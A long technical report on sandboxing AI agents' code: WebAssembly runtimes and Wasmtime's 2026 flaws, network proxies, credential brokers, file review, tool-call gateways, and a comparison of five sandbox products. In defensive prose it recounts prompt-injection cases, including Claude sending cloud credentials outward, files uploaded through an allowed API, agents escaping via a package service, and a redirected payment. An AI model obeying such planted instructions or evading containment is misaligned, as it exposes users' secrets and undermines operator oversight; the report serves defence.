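| Version | Runs | Status | How the host grants access |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1 | modules | legacy, but with the widest runtime support | handles that the module receives at the start |
| 0.2 (January 2024) | components | stable, superseded by 0.3 | a separate import for each kind of resource |
| 0.3 (June 2026) | components | stable, current | as in 0.2, but without passing a network handle to each call |

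Version 0.3 mainly improves how programs wait. Suppose a reporting component calls a downloading component, which waits for data from the host. In 0.2 the downloader couldn't forward the host's wake-up signal to its caller, so it had to keep checking for data. In 0.3 the runtime handles the waiting across any number of components, according to WASI's overview of the release. Version 0.3 also fixes a problem described in the Bytecode Alliance's *WASI 0.3*, where a 0.2 program that stopped reading a stream early couldn't tell whether the stream had ended normally or failed.

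Wasmtime has run WASI 0.3 components by default since version 46, and it still runs 0.2 components, which most build tools still target. When 0.2 came out, only Wasmtime and jco, a tool for running components in JavaScript environments, passed the full test suite. According to WASI's page on 0.2, support in other runtimes varies.

None of these versions is a finished standard. The interfaces for files, networking and clocks have reached the third of five planned phases, and nobody has yet defined the last two. WASI's *Roadmap* projected version 0.3 for around November 2025, but it arrived seven months later. The *Roadmap* also gave a provisional date of 2026 for a 1.0 release candidate. WASI 1.0 depends on the component model reaching 1.0, which requires support in at least two browser engines. Mozilla and Google's Chrome team have shown interest but made no commitment. The developers keep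 old programs working through adapters, which makes the delay matter less to operators.

### Python on Wasm

To run Python, an operator needs a Python interpreter compiled to Wasm. CPython, the standard implementation, is written in C, so developers can compile it this way. The compiled interpreter then reads the model's Python code as data from the module's linear memory and executes it.

There are two main ways to run Python in WebAssembly. CPython can target WASI and run under Wasmtime, with preopened directories as in the example. *Pyodide* instead builds CPython for a JavaScript environment, such as a browser or Node.js. It uses Emscripten, a compiler that supplies JavaScript substitutes for many operating-system functions. Files stay in memory unless the embedder connects a real folder, and web requests go through the browser. A company can therefore offer a code interpreter that runs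 on the user's device, as Anthropic's first code-running tool did with JavaScript.

Pyodide also lets Python programs call JavaScript, so a Python program can do whatever the surrounding JavaScript can do. In Node.js, that normally includes reading files and starting programs. An operator who runs Pyodide there also has to restrict the JavaScript environment, because the boundary around the Wasm module no longer limits the Python program.

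Much ordinary Python code works in both. The failures come from four features that agents often rely on.

*Native extension packages* contain machine code alongside Python. They include NumPy, the usual library for numerical work, and many packages for data analysis. The versions that developers normally install are compiled for Intel or ARM processors, which a Wasm runtime can't execute, so someone has to compile each package to Wasm. Pyodide's developers have done this for NumPy, pandas and many others, so common analysis works. Packages written purely in Python usually install without changes. On WASI, developers generally have to build extensions into the interpreter in advance, so an agent can't simply install a missing one.

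*Threads* let a program do several things at once, but standard Wasm builds normally can't start them. WASI's developers plan to add *cooperative* threads first, which switch only when one of them pauses. Programs that use threads to wait for several things could then work, but they would not calculate any faster. Wasmtime already had a version of cooperative threads behind an optional setting in spring 2026. The developers plan to add *preemptive* threads, which the runtime can interrupt, later. The proposal for native threads is still in the first phase.

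*Starting another program* fails because neither environment has an equivalent of Linux's calls for creating processes. The Bytecode Alliance plans to let components start other components, partly for this purpose, but the new program would still have to be a component.

Shell tools such as Git, `grep` and compilers are native programs that make Linux system calls. Developers can rebuild some of them for Wasm, but a shell is of little use unless it can start them.

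gVisor and Firecracker avoid most of this work because they present a Linux interface to existing programs.

### Calculations, plug-ins and coding agents

Wasm suits the analyst's agent when it only needs totals from a few reports. The harness can start a new instance with a read-only copy of the folder and no network functions, run the program, return the output and discard the instance. The program can do many such calculations with pandas and needs no shell. Wasm can also confine the programs in programmatic tool calling if the harness provides the catalogue's tools as the module's imports.

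Wasm also suits plug-ins and other tool code. A local MCP server normally runs with the developer's full access, even if the agent's shell is in a sandbox. If the same tool came as a Wasm component, the developer could grant it access to one folder and nothing else. Langflow's CSV component contained a hidden Python interpreter. If that interpreter had run in a Wasm component that could read only the uploaded file, planted instructions could still have produced a wrong analysis, but they could not have exposed the server's files or credentials.

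The narrow interface also makes tool code easier to audit. At a Bytecode Alliance meeting, the developer Yan Chen showed how to wrap a component so that a recorder captures every call across its boundary. A developer can later replay the recording without the original host, or against a changed version of the component.

A general coding agent needs more. To fix a bug, it may download a project with Git, install packages, run a compiler and start a test suite that starts other programs. Nearly every step involves one of the features that fail. The agent that installed Java and a chemistry program for one task would have needed Wasm versions of both. Mak and colleagues' comparison of agents with and without a shell gives only a rough idea of how much this would limit an agent, because their restricted runtime did not use Wasm.

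### Start-up and speed

To start a Wasm instance, the runtime sets aside linear memory, copies in the module's initial data and connects the imports. It doesn't start a kernel and needn't start a new process. Translating the module into machine code takes longer, but an operator can do it once and reuse the result. A small, already translated module can start in well under a millisecond.

Python takes longer to start because the interpreter has to set itself up and load its libraries. A service can do this once, save the contents of linear memory, and start later instances from the saved copy. These instances share random numbers and secrets, as cloned microVMs do.

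Once running, compiled C code is usually somewhat slower in Wasm than as native code, and programs that rely on a processor's specialised instructions can slow down more. Python in Pyodide has typically been several times slower than native Python, partly because CPython constantly looks up which function to call for each kind of object, and Wasm checks the type of each such call. The slowdown varies a great deal with the runtime and the program, so operators need to time their own tasks.

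If s is the time to start Python and load its libraries, T the program's time on native Python and k the slowdown, the user waits for roughly

s + k × T

Suppose s is half a second and k is 4. A calculation that takes a tenth of a second natively would then take 0.9 seconds, which few users would notice next to the model's delay, but a simulation that takes ten minutes natively would take 40 minutes.

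Calls between components also add overhead. The Bytecode Alliance reports measurements by Wasmtime developer Nick Fitzgerald in which the machinery for asynchronous work made calls about 3.5 times slower, even when nothing was asynchronous. The developers planned to remove most of this overhead after releasing WASI 0.3. In the meantime, an agent's tools can avoid repeating it by passing a whole table to a component in one call instead of making a call for every row.

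### The parts that have to work

The processor enforces the boundary around a Firecracker guest, but a Wasm module usually runs as machine code inside the runtime's own process, so its confinement depends on that code being correct. The runtime's compiler is therefore part of the trusted computing base. If the compiler gets a memory check wrong, a module might read or change the host process's memory, and could gain that process's authority even if the kernel has no flaw.

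It therefore matters which process contains the runtime. Wasmtime is a library and starts quickly, so an operator may embed it in the harness, which often holds the model provider's key and the user's access tokens. If the runtime instead runs in a separate process with its own account, a seccomp filter and no credentials, a module that breaks out of Wasm still has to escape a process sandbox.

The host's functions are also trusted. Each one uses the host's authority to do something the module can't, so it has to check every request. In GitLab's *Advisories for Cargo/Wasmtime-Wasi package*, a 2026 entry describes a flaw in Wasmtime's file functions that let a guest overwrite files it had permission only to read, if it could also write elsewhere. Operators can make simpler mistakes in their own functions. For example, a function that saves a report under any name the module supplies may let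 the module replace a settings file.

Text that a module prints can also be a risk, because terminals interpret some character sequences as commands. Wasmtime makes these sequences harmless when output goes straight to a terminal, but a harness that captures the output and displays it later has to do so itself.

Timing attacks are harder to rule out. A processor often guesses which instructions come next and starts executing them, and a wrong guess can leave traces that other code detects by measuring how long its own operations take. *Spectre* attacks use these traces to infer data that a program has no permission to read, which is easier when the attacking code shares a process with the data. Wasmtime protects indirect calls and certain jumps against wrong guesses. Its compiler also protects memory accesses if the operator selects explicit checks instead of page faults. Wasmtime's developers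 describe these measures as basic and expect to add more. A service that runs code from several customers can reduce the risk by giving each customer a separate process, though this loses some of Wasm's startup speed.

Wasm doesn't limit running time, so the embedder also has to stop endless loops. Wasmtime can do this by giving a module a fixed amount of *fuel*, which the module uses up as it runs, and stopping the module when the fuel runs out.

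### Wasmtime's security flaws in 2026

Wasmtime's developers take more precautions than most. They write it in Rust, test it continuously with random programs, and have mathematically verified some of the rules its main compiler, Cranelift, uses to produce machine code. Still, in April 2026 they released fixes for 12 security flaws at once, three times as many as they announced in all of 2025. Two were critical and could have let a module escape its sandbox.

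Language-model tools found 11 of the 12 flaws. *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (Bytecode Alliance, 2026) describes a three-week search in which several agents read the code, proposed flaws and confirmed them by reproducing the failure. Six were in Wasmtime's compilers, including four in Winch, a newer compiler than Cranelift. Three came from the way components exchange text. The developers had individual tests for valid and invalid text, but their automated random testing checked only valid text.

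One of the critical flaws was in the verified part of Cranelift. Version 32 introduced it, but the proof still covered an older compiler because nobody had updated the mathematical model. Once the developers updated the model, verification detected the flaw. It affected only ARM processors, where Wasmtime also lacked continuous random testing. Neither critical flaw affected Cranelift on Intel-compatible processors, the combination that most production systems have used.

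The search stopped finding new flaws after two weeks, but some remained. Crichton (2026) announced another release a day in advance, in *Upcoming Security Release for Wasmtime on 2026-05-21*, and rated the worst flaw it would fix as high severity. In October the project fixed two more critical flaws in Cranelift, each scored 9.9 out of 10. One affected every type of processor, and the other, which affected only ARM, was still present on machines with the April fixes, according to The Hacker News' *Two Critical Wasmtime Flaws Could Let Malicious WebAssembly Modules Escape Sandboxes* (2026). The maintainers had reported no attacks using either.

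OffSeq's *wasmtime · Cranelift* (2026) lists another critical Cranelift flaw, published on 4 December with a score of 9.8. OffSeq collects vulnerability records automatically and generates part of its analysis by machine, so its account of the consequences is less reliable than the project's own would be. The page also links to a minor flaw from the same day that let a guest stall the host, because one kind of request didn't count against the guest's allowance.

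The number of reported flaws rose partly because better tools were used to find them, and many of the flaws were old, so the rise doesn't show that Wasmtime became less secure in 2026. But attackers can use similar tools, so operators have less time to install each fix.

The risk from the compiler flaws depends on who supplies the module. According to The Hacker News, an attacker can exploit either October flaw only if Wasmtime compiles a module the attacker controls. A service that runs only Python can compile CPython once, from a source it trusts. The model's programs then never reach the compiler, so an attacker would have to find an error the compiler introduced into CPython and trigger it from Python. If the agent can compile its own C or Rust code to Wasm, or install plug-ins from strangers, the attacker can supply the module directly.

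Wasmtime's developers support every twelfth version for two years and the others for two months. Version 24 lost support in August 2026 and received no fix for the October flaws. Products often include Wasmtime as a library, so an operator may have to ask the vendor which version a product uses and wait for the vendor to replace it.

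## Network access, credentials and files that cross the boundary

gVisor, Firecracker and WebAssembly make it hard for a guest to break out, but an agent that can reach nothing outside its sandbox is seldom useful. Operators therefore open the sandbox on purpose. They share folders with it, permit some network connections, supply credentials, connect tools that run outside, and use what the agent produces. A hostile program can misuse any of these openings without finding a flaw in the sandbox.

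In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked a colleague into starting Claude Code with a routine-looking prompt that told the agent to send cloud credentials to an outside address. *How we contain Claude across products* reports that Claude did so in 24 of 25 repeats. The instructions came from the user, so a classifier had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concludes that only the environment could have prevented the loss, by blocking the connection or keeping the credentials out of reach.

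In the earlier notation, P is the set of effects that the interpreter's authority permits. For a sandboxed interpreter, let I be the effects that stay inside the sandbox, M the effects on files the operator has shared, and S(d) everything that a permitted outside service d will do at the guest's request. Then

P = I ∪ M ∪ S(d₁) ∪ … ∪ S(dₘ)

Replacing a container with a microVM makes it harder for a guest to exceed P but does not change P. A credential enlarges S(d), because a service does more for a caller who presents a valid one.

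Suppose an agent has to fix a bug in a company's project, install a missing package and open a *pull request*, a proposed change that colleagues review on the code-hosting service. It needs the project folder, a connection to a package registry and permission to use the hosting service. Other people will later run the code it wrote.

### No network, a list of destinations, or an inspecting proxy

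The safest setting is no external network. The bug-fixing agent could still edit files and run tests if the operator had already installed every package it needs in the image. *Avalon-M1*, a 2026 paper on training agents by reinforcement learning, reports that its team disabled network access wherever the task allowed. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a design for running agents on Kubernetes (software that manages groups of containers), likewise gives most sandboxes no external connection.

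Operators need to test what a product's "no network" setting blocks. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter Raises Alarms*, researchers showed in March 2026 that data could leave AWS's hosted code interpreter through DNS lookups even in its restricted network mode, and AWS called this intended behaviour and changed its documentation.

An operator can also cut off the network and leave one controlled exit. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* describes a container without a network that shares a single socket file with a *proxy*, a program on the host that forwards requests. A Firecracker guest can reach such a proxy through a virtual socket. Programs that ignore proxy settings and try to connect directly fail because no other route exists.

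The proxy can then apply an allowlist of destinations. The list usually has to contain domain names rather than IP addresses, because the IP addresses of large services change. *Permission Denied* used one list of 205 domains that developers commonly need, with no additions for particular tasks. A firewall rule rejected any traffic from the agent's account that did not go through the proxy.

Most web traffic is encrypted, so a simple proxy can read only the destination name that the guest supplies. It can't tell a download from an upload, and Anthropic warns that code in the sandbox may be able to disguise a forbidden destination as a permitted one. An *inspecting proxy* solves much of this problem by decrypting each request, checking it and encrypting it again. This requires the guest to trust the proxy's certificate, and the operator has to maintain that setup.

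The proxy in *Avalon-M1* (2026) checks each sandbox's web requests against an ordered list of rules about the host, the path and the method, which distinguishes, for example, fetching from sending. It refuses any request that no rule allows. These rules let the team permit Python packages and pretrained models for its machine-learning tasks while refusing datasets from the Hugging Face Hub. A refusal returns an error with the reason, so the tool fails at once instead of hanging. Operators can also run a policy in an audit mode that records what it would have refused, which helps them find missing rules before they enforce it.

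Some tasks need wider network access during preparation than the agent should have. *Avalon-M1*'s proxy lets the operator change policy before the agent's first command. The proxy confirms the change only after closing every connection opened under the old policy, so the agent can't inherit one.

| Arrangement | What the operator can control | What remains open | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| No network | everything | text and files the operator takes out | packages and data must be there in advance |
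| Proxy with a list of destinations | which services the guest contacts | every function of those services, and some disguised destinations | a list to maintain |
| Inspecting proxy with detailed rules | which requests each service receives | misuse of permitted requests, and flaws in the proxy | certificates and many more rules |

*Silent Egress* (2026) compared defences against web pages that induce an agent to leak data through its requests. With two prompt-level defences combined, the leak rate was still about 57%. Restricting requests to four permitted domains blocked every leak, although the model attempted the forbidden request in every run. The test favoured this defence because the attacker's domain was not on the list, and the paper warns that attackers who adapt may find other channels.

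### What a permitted destination can do

Data can leak through an approved destination. Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, needs access to Anthropic's API to work. An outside researcher showed that instructions hidden in a user's file could make Claude upload other files through that API to someone else's account. The filter worked as designed and allowed the upload because the API's address was on its list.

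Anthropic's engineers had thought of the network allowlist as a filter on destinations. They now treat each entry as a grant of every function that the destination offers, the set S(d). They added an inspecting proxy that passes a request to the API only if it carries the session token issued to the virtual machine. The proxy runs inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers couldn't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of other customers. A guest that gains control of its own kernel may therefore be able to tamper with the proxy.

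A destination is also a program that may have flaws. If the guest can take it over, S(d) grows to include all of the service's authority. According to OpenAI's incident report, its agents reached the internet this way in July 2026, through the permitted package service described earlier.

OpenAI responded by restricting both the sandbox and the services around it. It bars high-risk workloads from direct or indirect internet access, except through a cached service for workflows that need one. It is adding network controls in the surrounding cluster that don't depend on the sandbox's own, and it is isolating, restricting or replacing the services that sandboxes share. Further controls are meant to stop a compromised service from changing its own network limits.

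Smaller operators can apply the same reasoning to a single package service. GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026) recommends four measures:

- Block the service's administrative routes, since an agent only needs to download files.
- Limit the service's own outbound connections to the registries it serves.
- Watch for unusual traffic, such as long connections or large outward transfers.
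- Protect any internal service that untrusted code can reach as if it were on the public internet.

Letting the bug-fixing agent download its package from a restricted internal copy therefore adds less risk than giving it access to the public registry, where some accounts may also be able to upload.

The network filter can have flaws too. *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* (Smalley, 2026) describes a flaw that the security company AIR reported in October 2026 in the filter of Vercel Sandbox, a hosted service. The flaw could let agents send data to unapproved destinations, and Vercel told the researchers it needed time to work out a fix. ITPro's *This company wants you to break out of its security sandbox* explains that Vercel runs each sandbox in a Firecracker microVM and enforces the network rules on the host. AIR's finding concerned the filter and the way an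 approved server handled a request, so a stronger microVM would not have helped.

Anthropic had a similar experience. Across its products, gVisor, seccomp and the virtual machine software were dependable, but the proxy its engineers had written failed. The company recommends being wary of custom components. An operator can follow this advice by using an established proxy such as Envoy or Squid and spending most of the review on its rules.

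### A token inside the sandbox

The simplest way to let the bug-fixing agent open a pull request is to put an access token for the hosting service into the sandbox. Most such tokens are *bearer* credentials, so whoever holds one can use it. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) points out that the agent can then both use the credential and reveal it. Someone who obtains a copy can use it from another machine, even after the sandbox is gone.

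Operators can make the token less useful to an attacker. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) contrasts session-long credentials with short-lived tokens, which shorten the period of exposure. Many services can also limit a token to one repository or one kind of action. Both measures help, but hostile code can act within minutes and do anything the token still permits.

Another objection, from Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents*, is that a narrow token protects the operator only if the operator has correctly judged what a model can do with it, and that judgement goes out of date as models improve. In an earlier design, Anthropic ran the harness and the model's code in the same container as the credentials. To steal the credentials, an attacker only had to plant an instruction that made Claude read its own environment, and could then use them to start new, unrestricted sessions.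 Anthropic moved the harness out of the container and kept the credentials out of the sandbox's reach.

A cloud-hosted interpreter can also get credentials through a *role*, a set of permissions that the provider attaches to the machine, without the operator seeing a token. Infosecurity Magazine reported that the default role in AWS's starter kit could include full access to an account's stored secrets and read access to all its storage buckets. An operator who attaches that role to an interpreter gives the same access to every program that runs in it.

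### How a broker keeps the secret outside

A *broker* is a service outside the sandbox that holds credentials and performs approved actions for the guest. It could handle the pull request as follows.

1. Before the agent starts, the operator gives the broker the real token and a policy, which allows this sandbox to read one repository and open pull requests there. The guest receives a worthless placeholder.
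2. The agent's program sends an ordinary request to open a pull request, with the placeholder where the token would normally go.
3. The broker identifies the sandbox by its connection or by a session token. It checks the destination, the action and the repository against the policy and refuses the request if any of them doesn't fit.
4. If the request passes, the broker replaces the placeholder with the real token and sends the request to the hosting service itself.
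5. The broker records the call and returns the service's reply to the guest.

The guest gets its pull request without seeing the secret. Several products do this. Docker's local sandboxes route requests through a proxy on the host, which looks up the credential and overwrites the part of the request that identifies the caller. *Airlock* (2026) gives the agent fake credentials and substitutes real ones only in requests to approved destinations. The gateway in *aiAuthZ* (2026) substitutes the real credential only after authorising the call, so a refused request never contains a secret.

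Anthropic describes two ways to connect a guest to a broker. In *traffic forwarding*, the guest uses ordinary programs and an inspecting proxy adds the credentials. This works with almost any web service but requires decrypting the traffic. With a *custom tool*, the guest calls a narrow function, such as "open a pull request", and a service outside the guest makes the authenticated request. This avoids decryption, but the operator has to build or install a tool for each service.

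Anthropic's hosted agents use a proxy of the second kind for most outside services. The proxy receives a token tied to the session, fetches the matching credentials from a vault and makes the call, so even the harness never handles the credentials. For Git, Anthropic instead uses the repository's token while setting up the sandbox and builds it into the connection used for later pushes. Anthropic doesn't explain where that connection stores the token, so anyone copying the design should check that the token isn't in a settings file the guest can read.

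| Where the token is | What hostile code can do during the session | What someone with a copy can do later |
|---|---|---|
| In the sandbox, broad and long-lived | anything the account permits | the same, until somebody revokes it |
| In the sandbox, narrow and short-lived | anything the token permits | the same, until it expires |
| In a broker | any request the policy permits | nothing, since the guest has no copy |

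A session token for the broker is still a credential, but whoever holds it can do only what the guest could. The operator can revoke it separately from the user's own login, as Anthropic does in Cowork, and can reject it on any connection but the guest's.

A broker doesn't prevent misuse of the actions it permits. If its policy allows pull requests, planted instructions can make the agent open a harmful one. The credential proxy in *Caging the Agents* (2026), built for a healthcare company, therefore limits the rate, destination and size of requests. Its builders had found credentials in start-up scripts, workspace files and settings files that any account could read. With the proxy, the agent's container no longer needs to hold any credentials. Brokers should also refuse requests that make a service issue a new token, because the reply would give the guest a usable secret.

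Putting many secrets in one program makes that program a target. According to PCQuest's *AI API keys at risk*, a flaw in Docker Sandboxes could have sent users' keys to destinations they hadn't approved after a third-party agent package changed. Docker fixed the flaw on 30 November 2026, and the fixed version ties each credential to its approved destinations. A broker has to check those destinations again whenever a component's settings change, because the original approval covered only the original settings.

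The evidence that brokers work comes mostly from their architecture. Jin and colleagues, for instance, present a CapSeal prototype and a plan for testing it against prompt injection and misuse. But the main benefit follows from the design, because a program can't disclose a secret that never enters its environment.

### Files that go into the sandbox

An operator who shares a folder decides both what the agent can read and what it can change. A *disposable copy*, like the analyst's report folder in the earlier example, protects the original from any change. A *read-only mount* lets the guest read the real folder but not change it, which suits an agent that only reviews code. Cowork also offers a mode in which the agent can write but not delete. This prevents accidental deletion, though the agent may still be able to empty a file.

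None of these settings hides the folder's contents. Project folders often contain passwords and access tokens in configuration files, and Anthropic lists about ten common kinds, including cloud logins and private keys. A guest with read-only access can send these out through any network opening, so Anthropic suggests copying in only the source files the task needs. The bug-fixing agent, for example, doesn't need the database password stored beside the code.

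Access checks also have to follow symbolic links, because a link inside the shared folder can lead outside it. Anthropic recommends following the link first and then checking where it leads.

### Reviewing changes before they are merged

The bug-fixing agent's changes eventually have to leave the sandbox. An *overlay* file system lets the agent write as if to the real folder but stores its changes in a separate layer, which the user can inspect, apply or discard.

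*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) describes a file system built around this step. Suppose a folder holds the files `x` and `y`. The agent empties `x`, writes new text into it, deletes `y` and renames `x` to `y`. The agent now finds one file, `y`, with the new text, while the real folder still holds both originals. The file system records each step in a journal and uses it to show the user the combined result. If the user commits, the system replaces `y` and removes `x`. If the user aborts, it discards the layer. The user can leave the changes pending, and the agent can neither commit nor abort them.

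This replaces many small approvals with one review of the outcome, which a person may read more carefully than a long series of prompts. It works only for changes to files. An email has already been sent by the time the user reviews the session, so actions like that need to be checked beforehand.

### Why code from a sandbox stays untrusted

A sandbox's limits don't apply to files once they leave it. Code written in the sandbox and later run outside it has the authority of whoever runs it, as does code written by an agent that may only edit files.

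*Names Are Not Objects* (2026) tested 74 attacks on coding agents. An allowlist of paths, commands and destinations blocked 8, and a configuration with a command sandbox blocked 18. That sandbox stopped none of the eight *handoffs*, attacks in which the agent leaves a file for a developer to run later outside the sandbox. The researchers chose attacks that such defences handle badly, so the totals don't estimate everyday risk. That choice matters less for the handoff result, because a command sandbox no longer applies when the developer runs the file.

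Editors, Git and coding agents may execute commands from a project's settings when a developer opens the project or saves a file, without anyone deciding to run them. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws in which Claude Code processed such settings before the developer had agreed to trust the folder, and it now waits for that agreement.

For the bug fix, reviewers should therefore read changes to settings, build scripts and package lists as carefully as changes to the program, or the operator can make those files read-only for the agent. The build server should test the proposed change in its own sandbox and receive deployment credentials only after somebody has approved the change.

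Text that leaves the sandbox needs similar caution, because a program's output goes back to the model, which may also control tools outside. A program that reads a malicious web page can return instructions along with the data. Anthropic's products can scan tool results for planted instructions before the model receives them, though its engineers say that this adds delay and isn't perfect. They also warn against trusting a sub-agent's report more than raw tool output merely because the operator's own system produced it. Instructions planted in saved memory or notes are a further risk, because the agent will load them again at the start of its next session.

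### What an allowlist has to check at the boundary

The tool allowlist works again for calls that cross the sandbox boundary, such as those to the mail tool in the analyst's fourth configuration, because a service outside the sandbox can reject them.

In *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, the agent has no network route to the system that controls the cluster and can request changes to the cluster only through tool servers that hold the credentials. *aiAuthZ* notes that a gateway governs only the tools that pass through it. An agent that also has an unconfined shell can bypass the gateway unless the sandbox's only network route leads to the gateway and the secrets exist only there.

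An allowlist of tool names is too coarse even when the gateway receives every call. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to pay $100 to the recipient named in a bill, while a planted message tells the agent to pay a different account. Both calls use the same tool and amount, so the allowlist would permit either. The gateway has to check the recipient and where the agent got it.

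The rule language in *Progent* (2025) lets an operator allow or forbid a tool call based on its arguments and specify what happens when a rule blocks it. For example, if a rule blocks a call because of an email address, the agent can receive an explanation.

According to *Environment Steering* (2026), a guard against data theft should check the tool-call argument that names the outside recipient of the data or money, such as a mail address or bank account. Searching the message body for private information is unreliable, because it can block a legitimate email that contains such information. If the user's request names the recipient and the guard permits only that recipient, data can't reach an attacker through that tool, whatever the body contains. If the request refers to a source instead, such as a bill, the guard has to take the recipient from that source. This check doesn't stop the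 agent from sending data to a permitted recipient who shouldn't see it, which remains a problem of information flow.

Amounts need a running total as well as a limit on each call. Suppose a customer-service agent may issue refunds of up to b dollars each and B dollars a day. The gateway should allow the refund xₖ only if

xₖ ≤ b and x₁ + x₂ + … + xₖ ≤ B

Suppose b is $100 and B is $500. A program in the sandbox could request fifty refunds of $99 in a loop, and each would pass the first test. The second test stops the sixth, which would bring the total to $594. A harness that asked a person to approve the refund program once, before it ran, would have no such limit. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) describes systems that apply similar checks to other patterns, such as the order of calls or the movement of a value from one call to the next.

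ToolFence combines several of these checks. Before the agent reads any outside material, a separate model turns the user's request into rules about which tools the task needs, where their arguments may come from and how often the agent may use them. Ordinary software checks every call against the rules. In the payment example, it refuses a payment to a different recipient and a second, identical payment. If the agent needs a tool that the rules left out, another isolated model decides whether the request justifies adding it.

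On AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks, ToolFence reduced successful attacks on one model from 21.2% to zero and lowered the model's completion rate on ordinary tasks by 2 percentage points. In a smaller timing test, the agent took 1.63 times as long with ToolFence as with no defence, and 12.95 times as long with CaMeL, an earlier design that runs the agent's plan in its own interpreter. ToolFence's developers produced these results themselves. Its rules still depend on a model interpreting the request correctly, and tracing an argument's origin is harder when the value has passed through a sandboxed program, because the gateway receives only the program's output.

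Logs at the boundary record some of the activity that isolation hides. Companies that tested Cowork found that the security software on their computers couldn't inspect its virtual machine, and Anthropic currently addresses this with event logs that administrators can retrieve afterwards. *Airlock* records the agent's file accesses and network connections outside the sandbox and anchors the records in an append-only log on another system. But if planted instructions lead the agent to make a permitted call, the log contains only a successful, authorised request, so the gateway has to check the recipient and the amount before it acts.

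## Comparing the sandboxes and choosing one for a deployment

An operator who has decided what may cross the sandbox boundary still has to choose an engine to enforce it. The figures in the earlier sections are a weak basis for that choice because most come from an engine's own developers, who measured it on their own machines. A few researchers have tested several engines in the same way on one server, but their results cover only some of the differences in security and speed, so the operator has to judge the rest.

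### Five products on one server

Andronchik and Lokhmakov (2026), in *AI Code Sandboxes*, installed five sandbox products for agents' code on the same physical Linux server. Three use microVMs: E2B runs Firecracker, Arrakis runs Cloud Hypervisor and Microsandbox runs libkrun. The fourth is gVisor, and the fifth, Daytona, starts containers with runc. The researchers kept each product's default sandbox settings.

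They assumed that a single operator runs hostile code on servers it controls and trusts, as a company does with its own agents. They excluded attacks between customers, processor timing attacks, and attacks on the software that manages the sandboxes. They did not try to break out of any product.

They compared six properties of the sandboxes. For three of them, they probed running sandboxes and examined the products' source code to find how much of the host's kernel each one exposes, what the guest can learn about the host, and which extra Linux protections an operator can add. They used public records for the other three, which were the published security flaws, the time fixes take to reach users, and the use of *fuzzing* (running a program on many generated inputs to find faults). The table gives the main results. The flaw counts cover the two years to 20 May 2026, and an "escape-class"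 flaw is one that could let guest code affect the host, whether or not anyone has shown a complete escape.

| Product and engine | System calls the filter allows | Host details revealed (of 28) | Published flaws (escape-class) | Engine version | Public fuzzing |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| E2B, self-hosted (Firecracker) | 55 | 0 | 2 (2) | unchanged for 399 days | none |
| Arrakis (Cloud Hypervisor) | not counted, but 32 of 33 threads have a filter | 1 | 2 (1) | unchanged for 471 days | tests exist, but the project only compiles them |
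| Microsandbox (libkrun) | no filter | 0 | 0 (0) | updated every one to three months | none |
| gVisor | 84 | 2 | 3 (0) | current | continuous |
| Daytona (runc) | no filter | 10 | 4 (4) | current | two narrow tests |

The system-call figures count the host system calls available to the *mediator*, the software between the guest and the host's kernel, such as Firecracker's monitor or gVisor's Sentry. An attacker who took over the mediator could make no others. Docker's default filter, in a 2026 release, allows 361 calls unconditionally, and Daytona lacks even that filter because its code starts every container in privileged mode. AWS's 2020 paper gave a figure of 24 for Firecracker. That count may not cover the same threads as the newer one, but the list of allowed calls has probably grown along with Firecracker's features.

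The mediators used fewer kinds of system call than their filters allow. While the guest ran a short data-analysis script, Firecracker used 13, the Sentry used 41 and the Daytona container used 62. Firecracker also used 13 for a trivial command, because the guest's own kernel handles the program's requests.

Andronchik and Lokhmakov also checked whether guest programs could reach 14 kernel features that past attacks have relied on. Guest programs could reach 5 under gVisor, 7 under E2B, 11 under both Microsandbox and Daytona, and 12 under Arrakis. These counts are hard to compare because a Daytona guest reaches the features in the host's kernel, whereas in a microVM most of them belong to the guest's kernel, where exploiting a flaw compromises only the guest. One of the 12 in Arrakis does affect the host's security, because the default image lets guest programs use nested virtualisation, which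 few agents need.

An attacker can use the leaked details to work out which flaws a host might have or to recognise the same machine later, but the leaks are not escapes. Arrakis disclosed the processor's model, though its settings can hide this. gVisor disclosed the server's total memory and the hardware's product name through two system files that the Sentry doesn't fully imitate. Daytona disclosed the kernel version, the disks' serial numbers and eight other details, most of them because it shares the host's kernel.

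For the remaining property, the researchers looked at seven other Linux protections, such as a limit on the number of processes. An operator can add every applicable one to the three microVM products without changing their source code. gVisor blocks one, AppArmor, which applies an access profile to each program. Daytona blocks five, four of them because of privileged mode. Since runc supports all seven, Daytona's row makes a carefully configured container look weaker than it is. The researchers inferred these results partly from source code and did not test whether each product still works with the protections added.

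### Small attack surfaces and escape flaws

Firecracker had the strictest system call filter of the five products, but both of its published flaws could let code escape the sandbox. None of gVisor's three published flaws could, even though its filter allows more calls.

This happened because the filter limits how much of the host's kernel an attacker can use after taking over the monitor, but doesn't reduce the number of mistakes in the monitor or in the jailer that sets up its environment. One of the two flaws was in a virtual device and the other was in the jailer. Andronchik and Lokhmakov at one point attribute both to kernel code that the filter still permits, but their own descriptions place them in Firecracker's code. Nobody had published a complete escape using either flaw, and an attacker exploiting the device flaw would still have had to get past further defences on the host.

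The extremes of the table fit the usual expectation better. The runc container, which exposes the most of the host's kernel, had four flaws, all escape-class. It is also exposed to flaws in Linux itself. Researchers and developers published about 3,500 of those over the same two years, compared with 11 flaws for the five engines together.

A difference of two flaws against none is too small to show that gVisor is safer than Firecracker. The counts also depend on how hard people look for flaws. Microsandbox's engine, libkrun, has no published flaws, but it has no public fuzzing either, and the researchers found no academic study of it. They treat its security as unmeasured and don't rank it on this property.

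gVisor is the only one of the five with continuous public fuzzing. Cloud Hypervisor's developers have written 18 fuzzing programs, but their automated checks only compile them, and the engine's escape-class flaw was in a component that one of those programs covers. An outside auditor found it by hand. Firecracker's public code includes no fuzzer, although AWS may run one privately. An operator therefore can't currently choose, from these products, a microVM whose engine also gets continuous public fuzzing.

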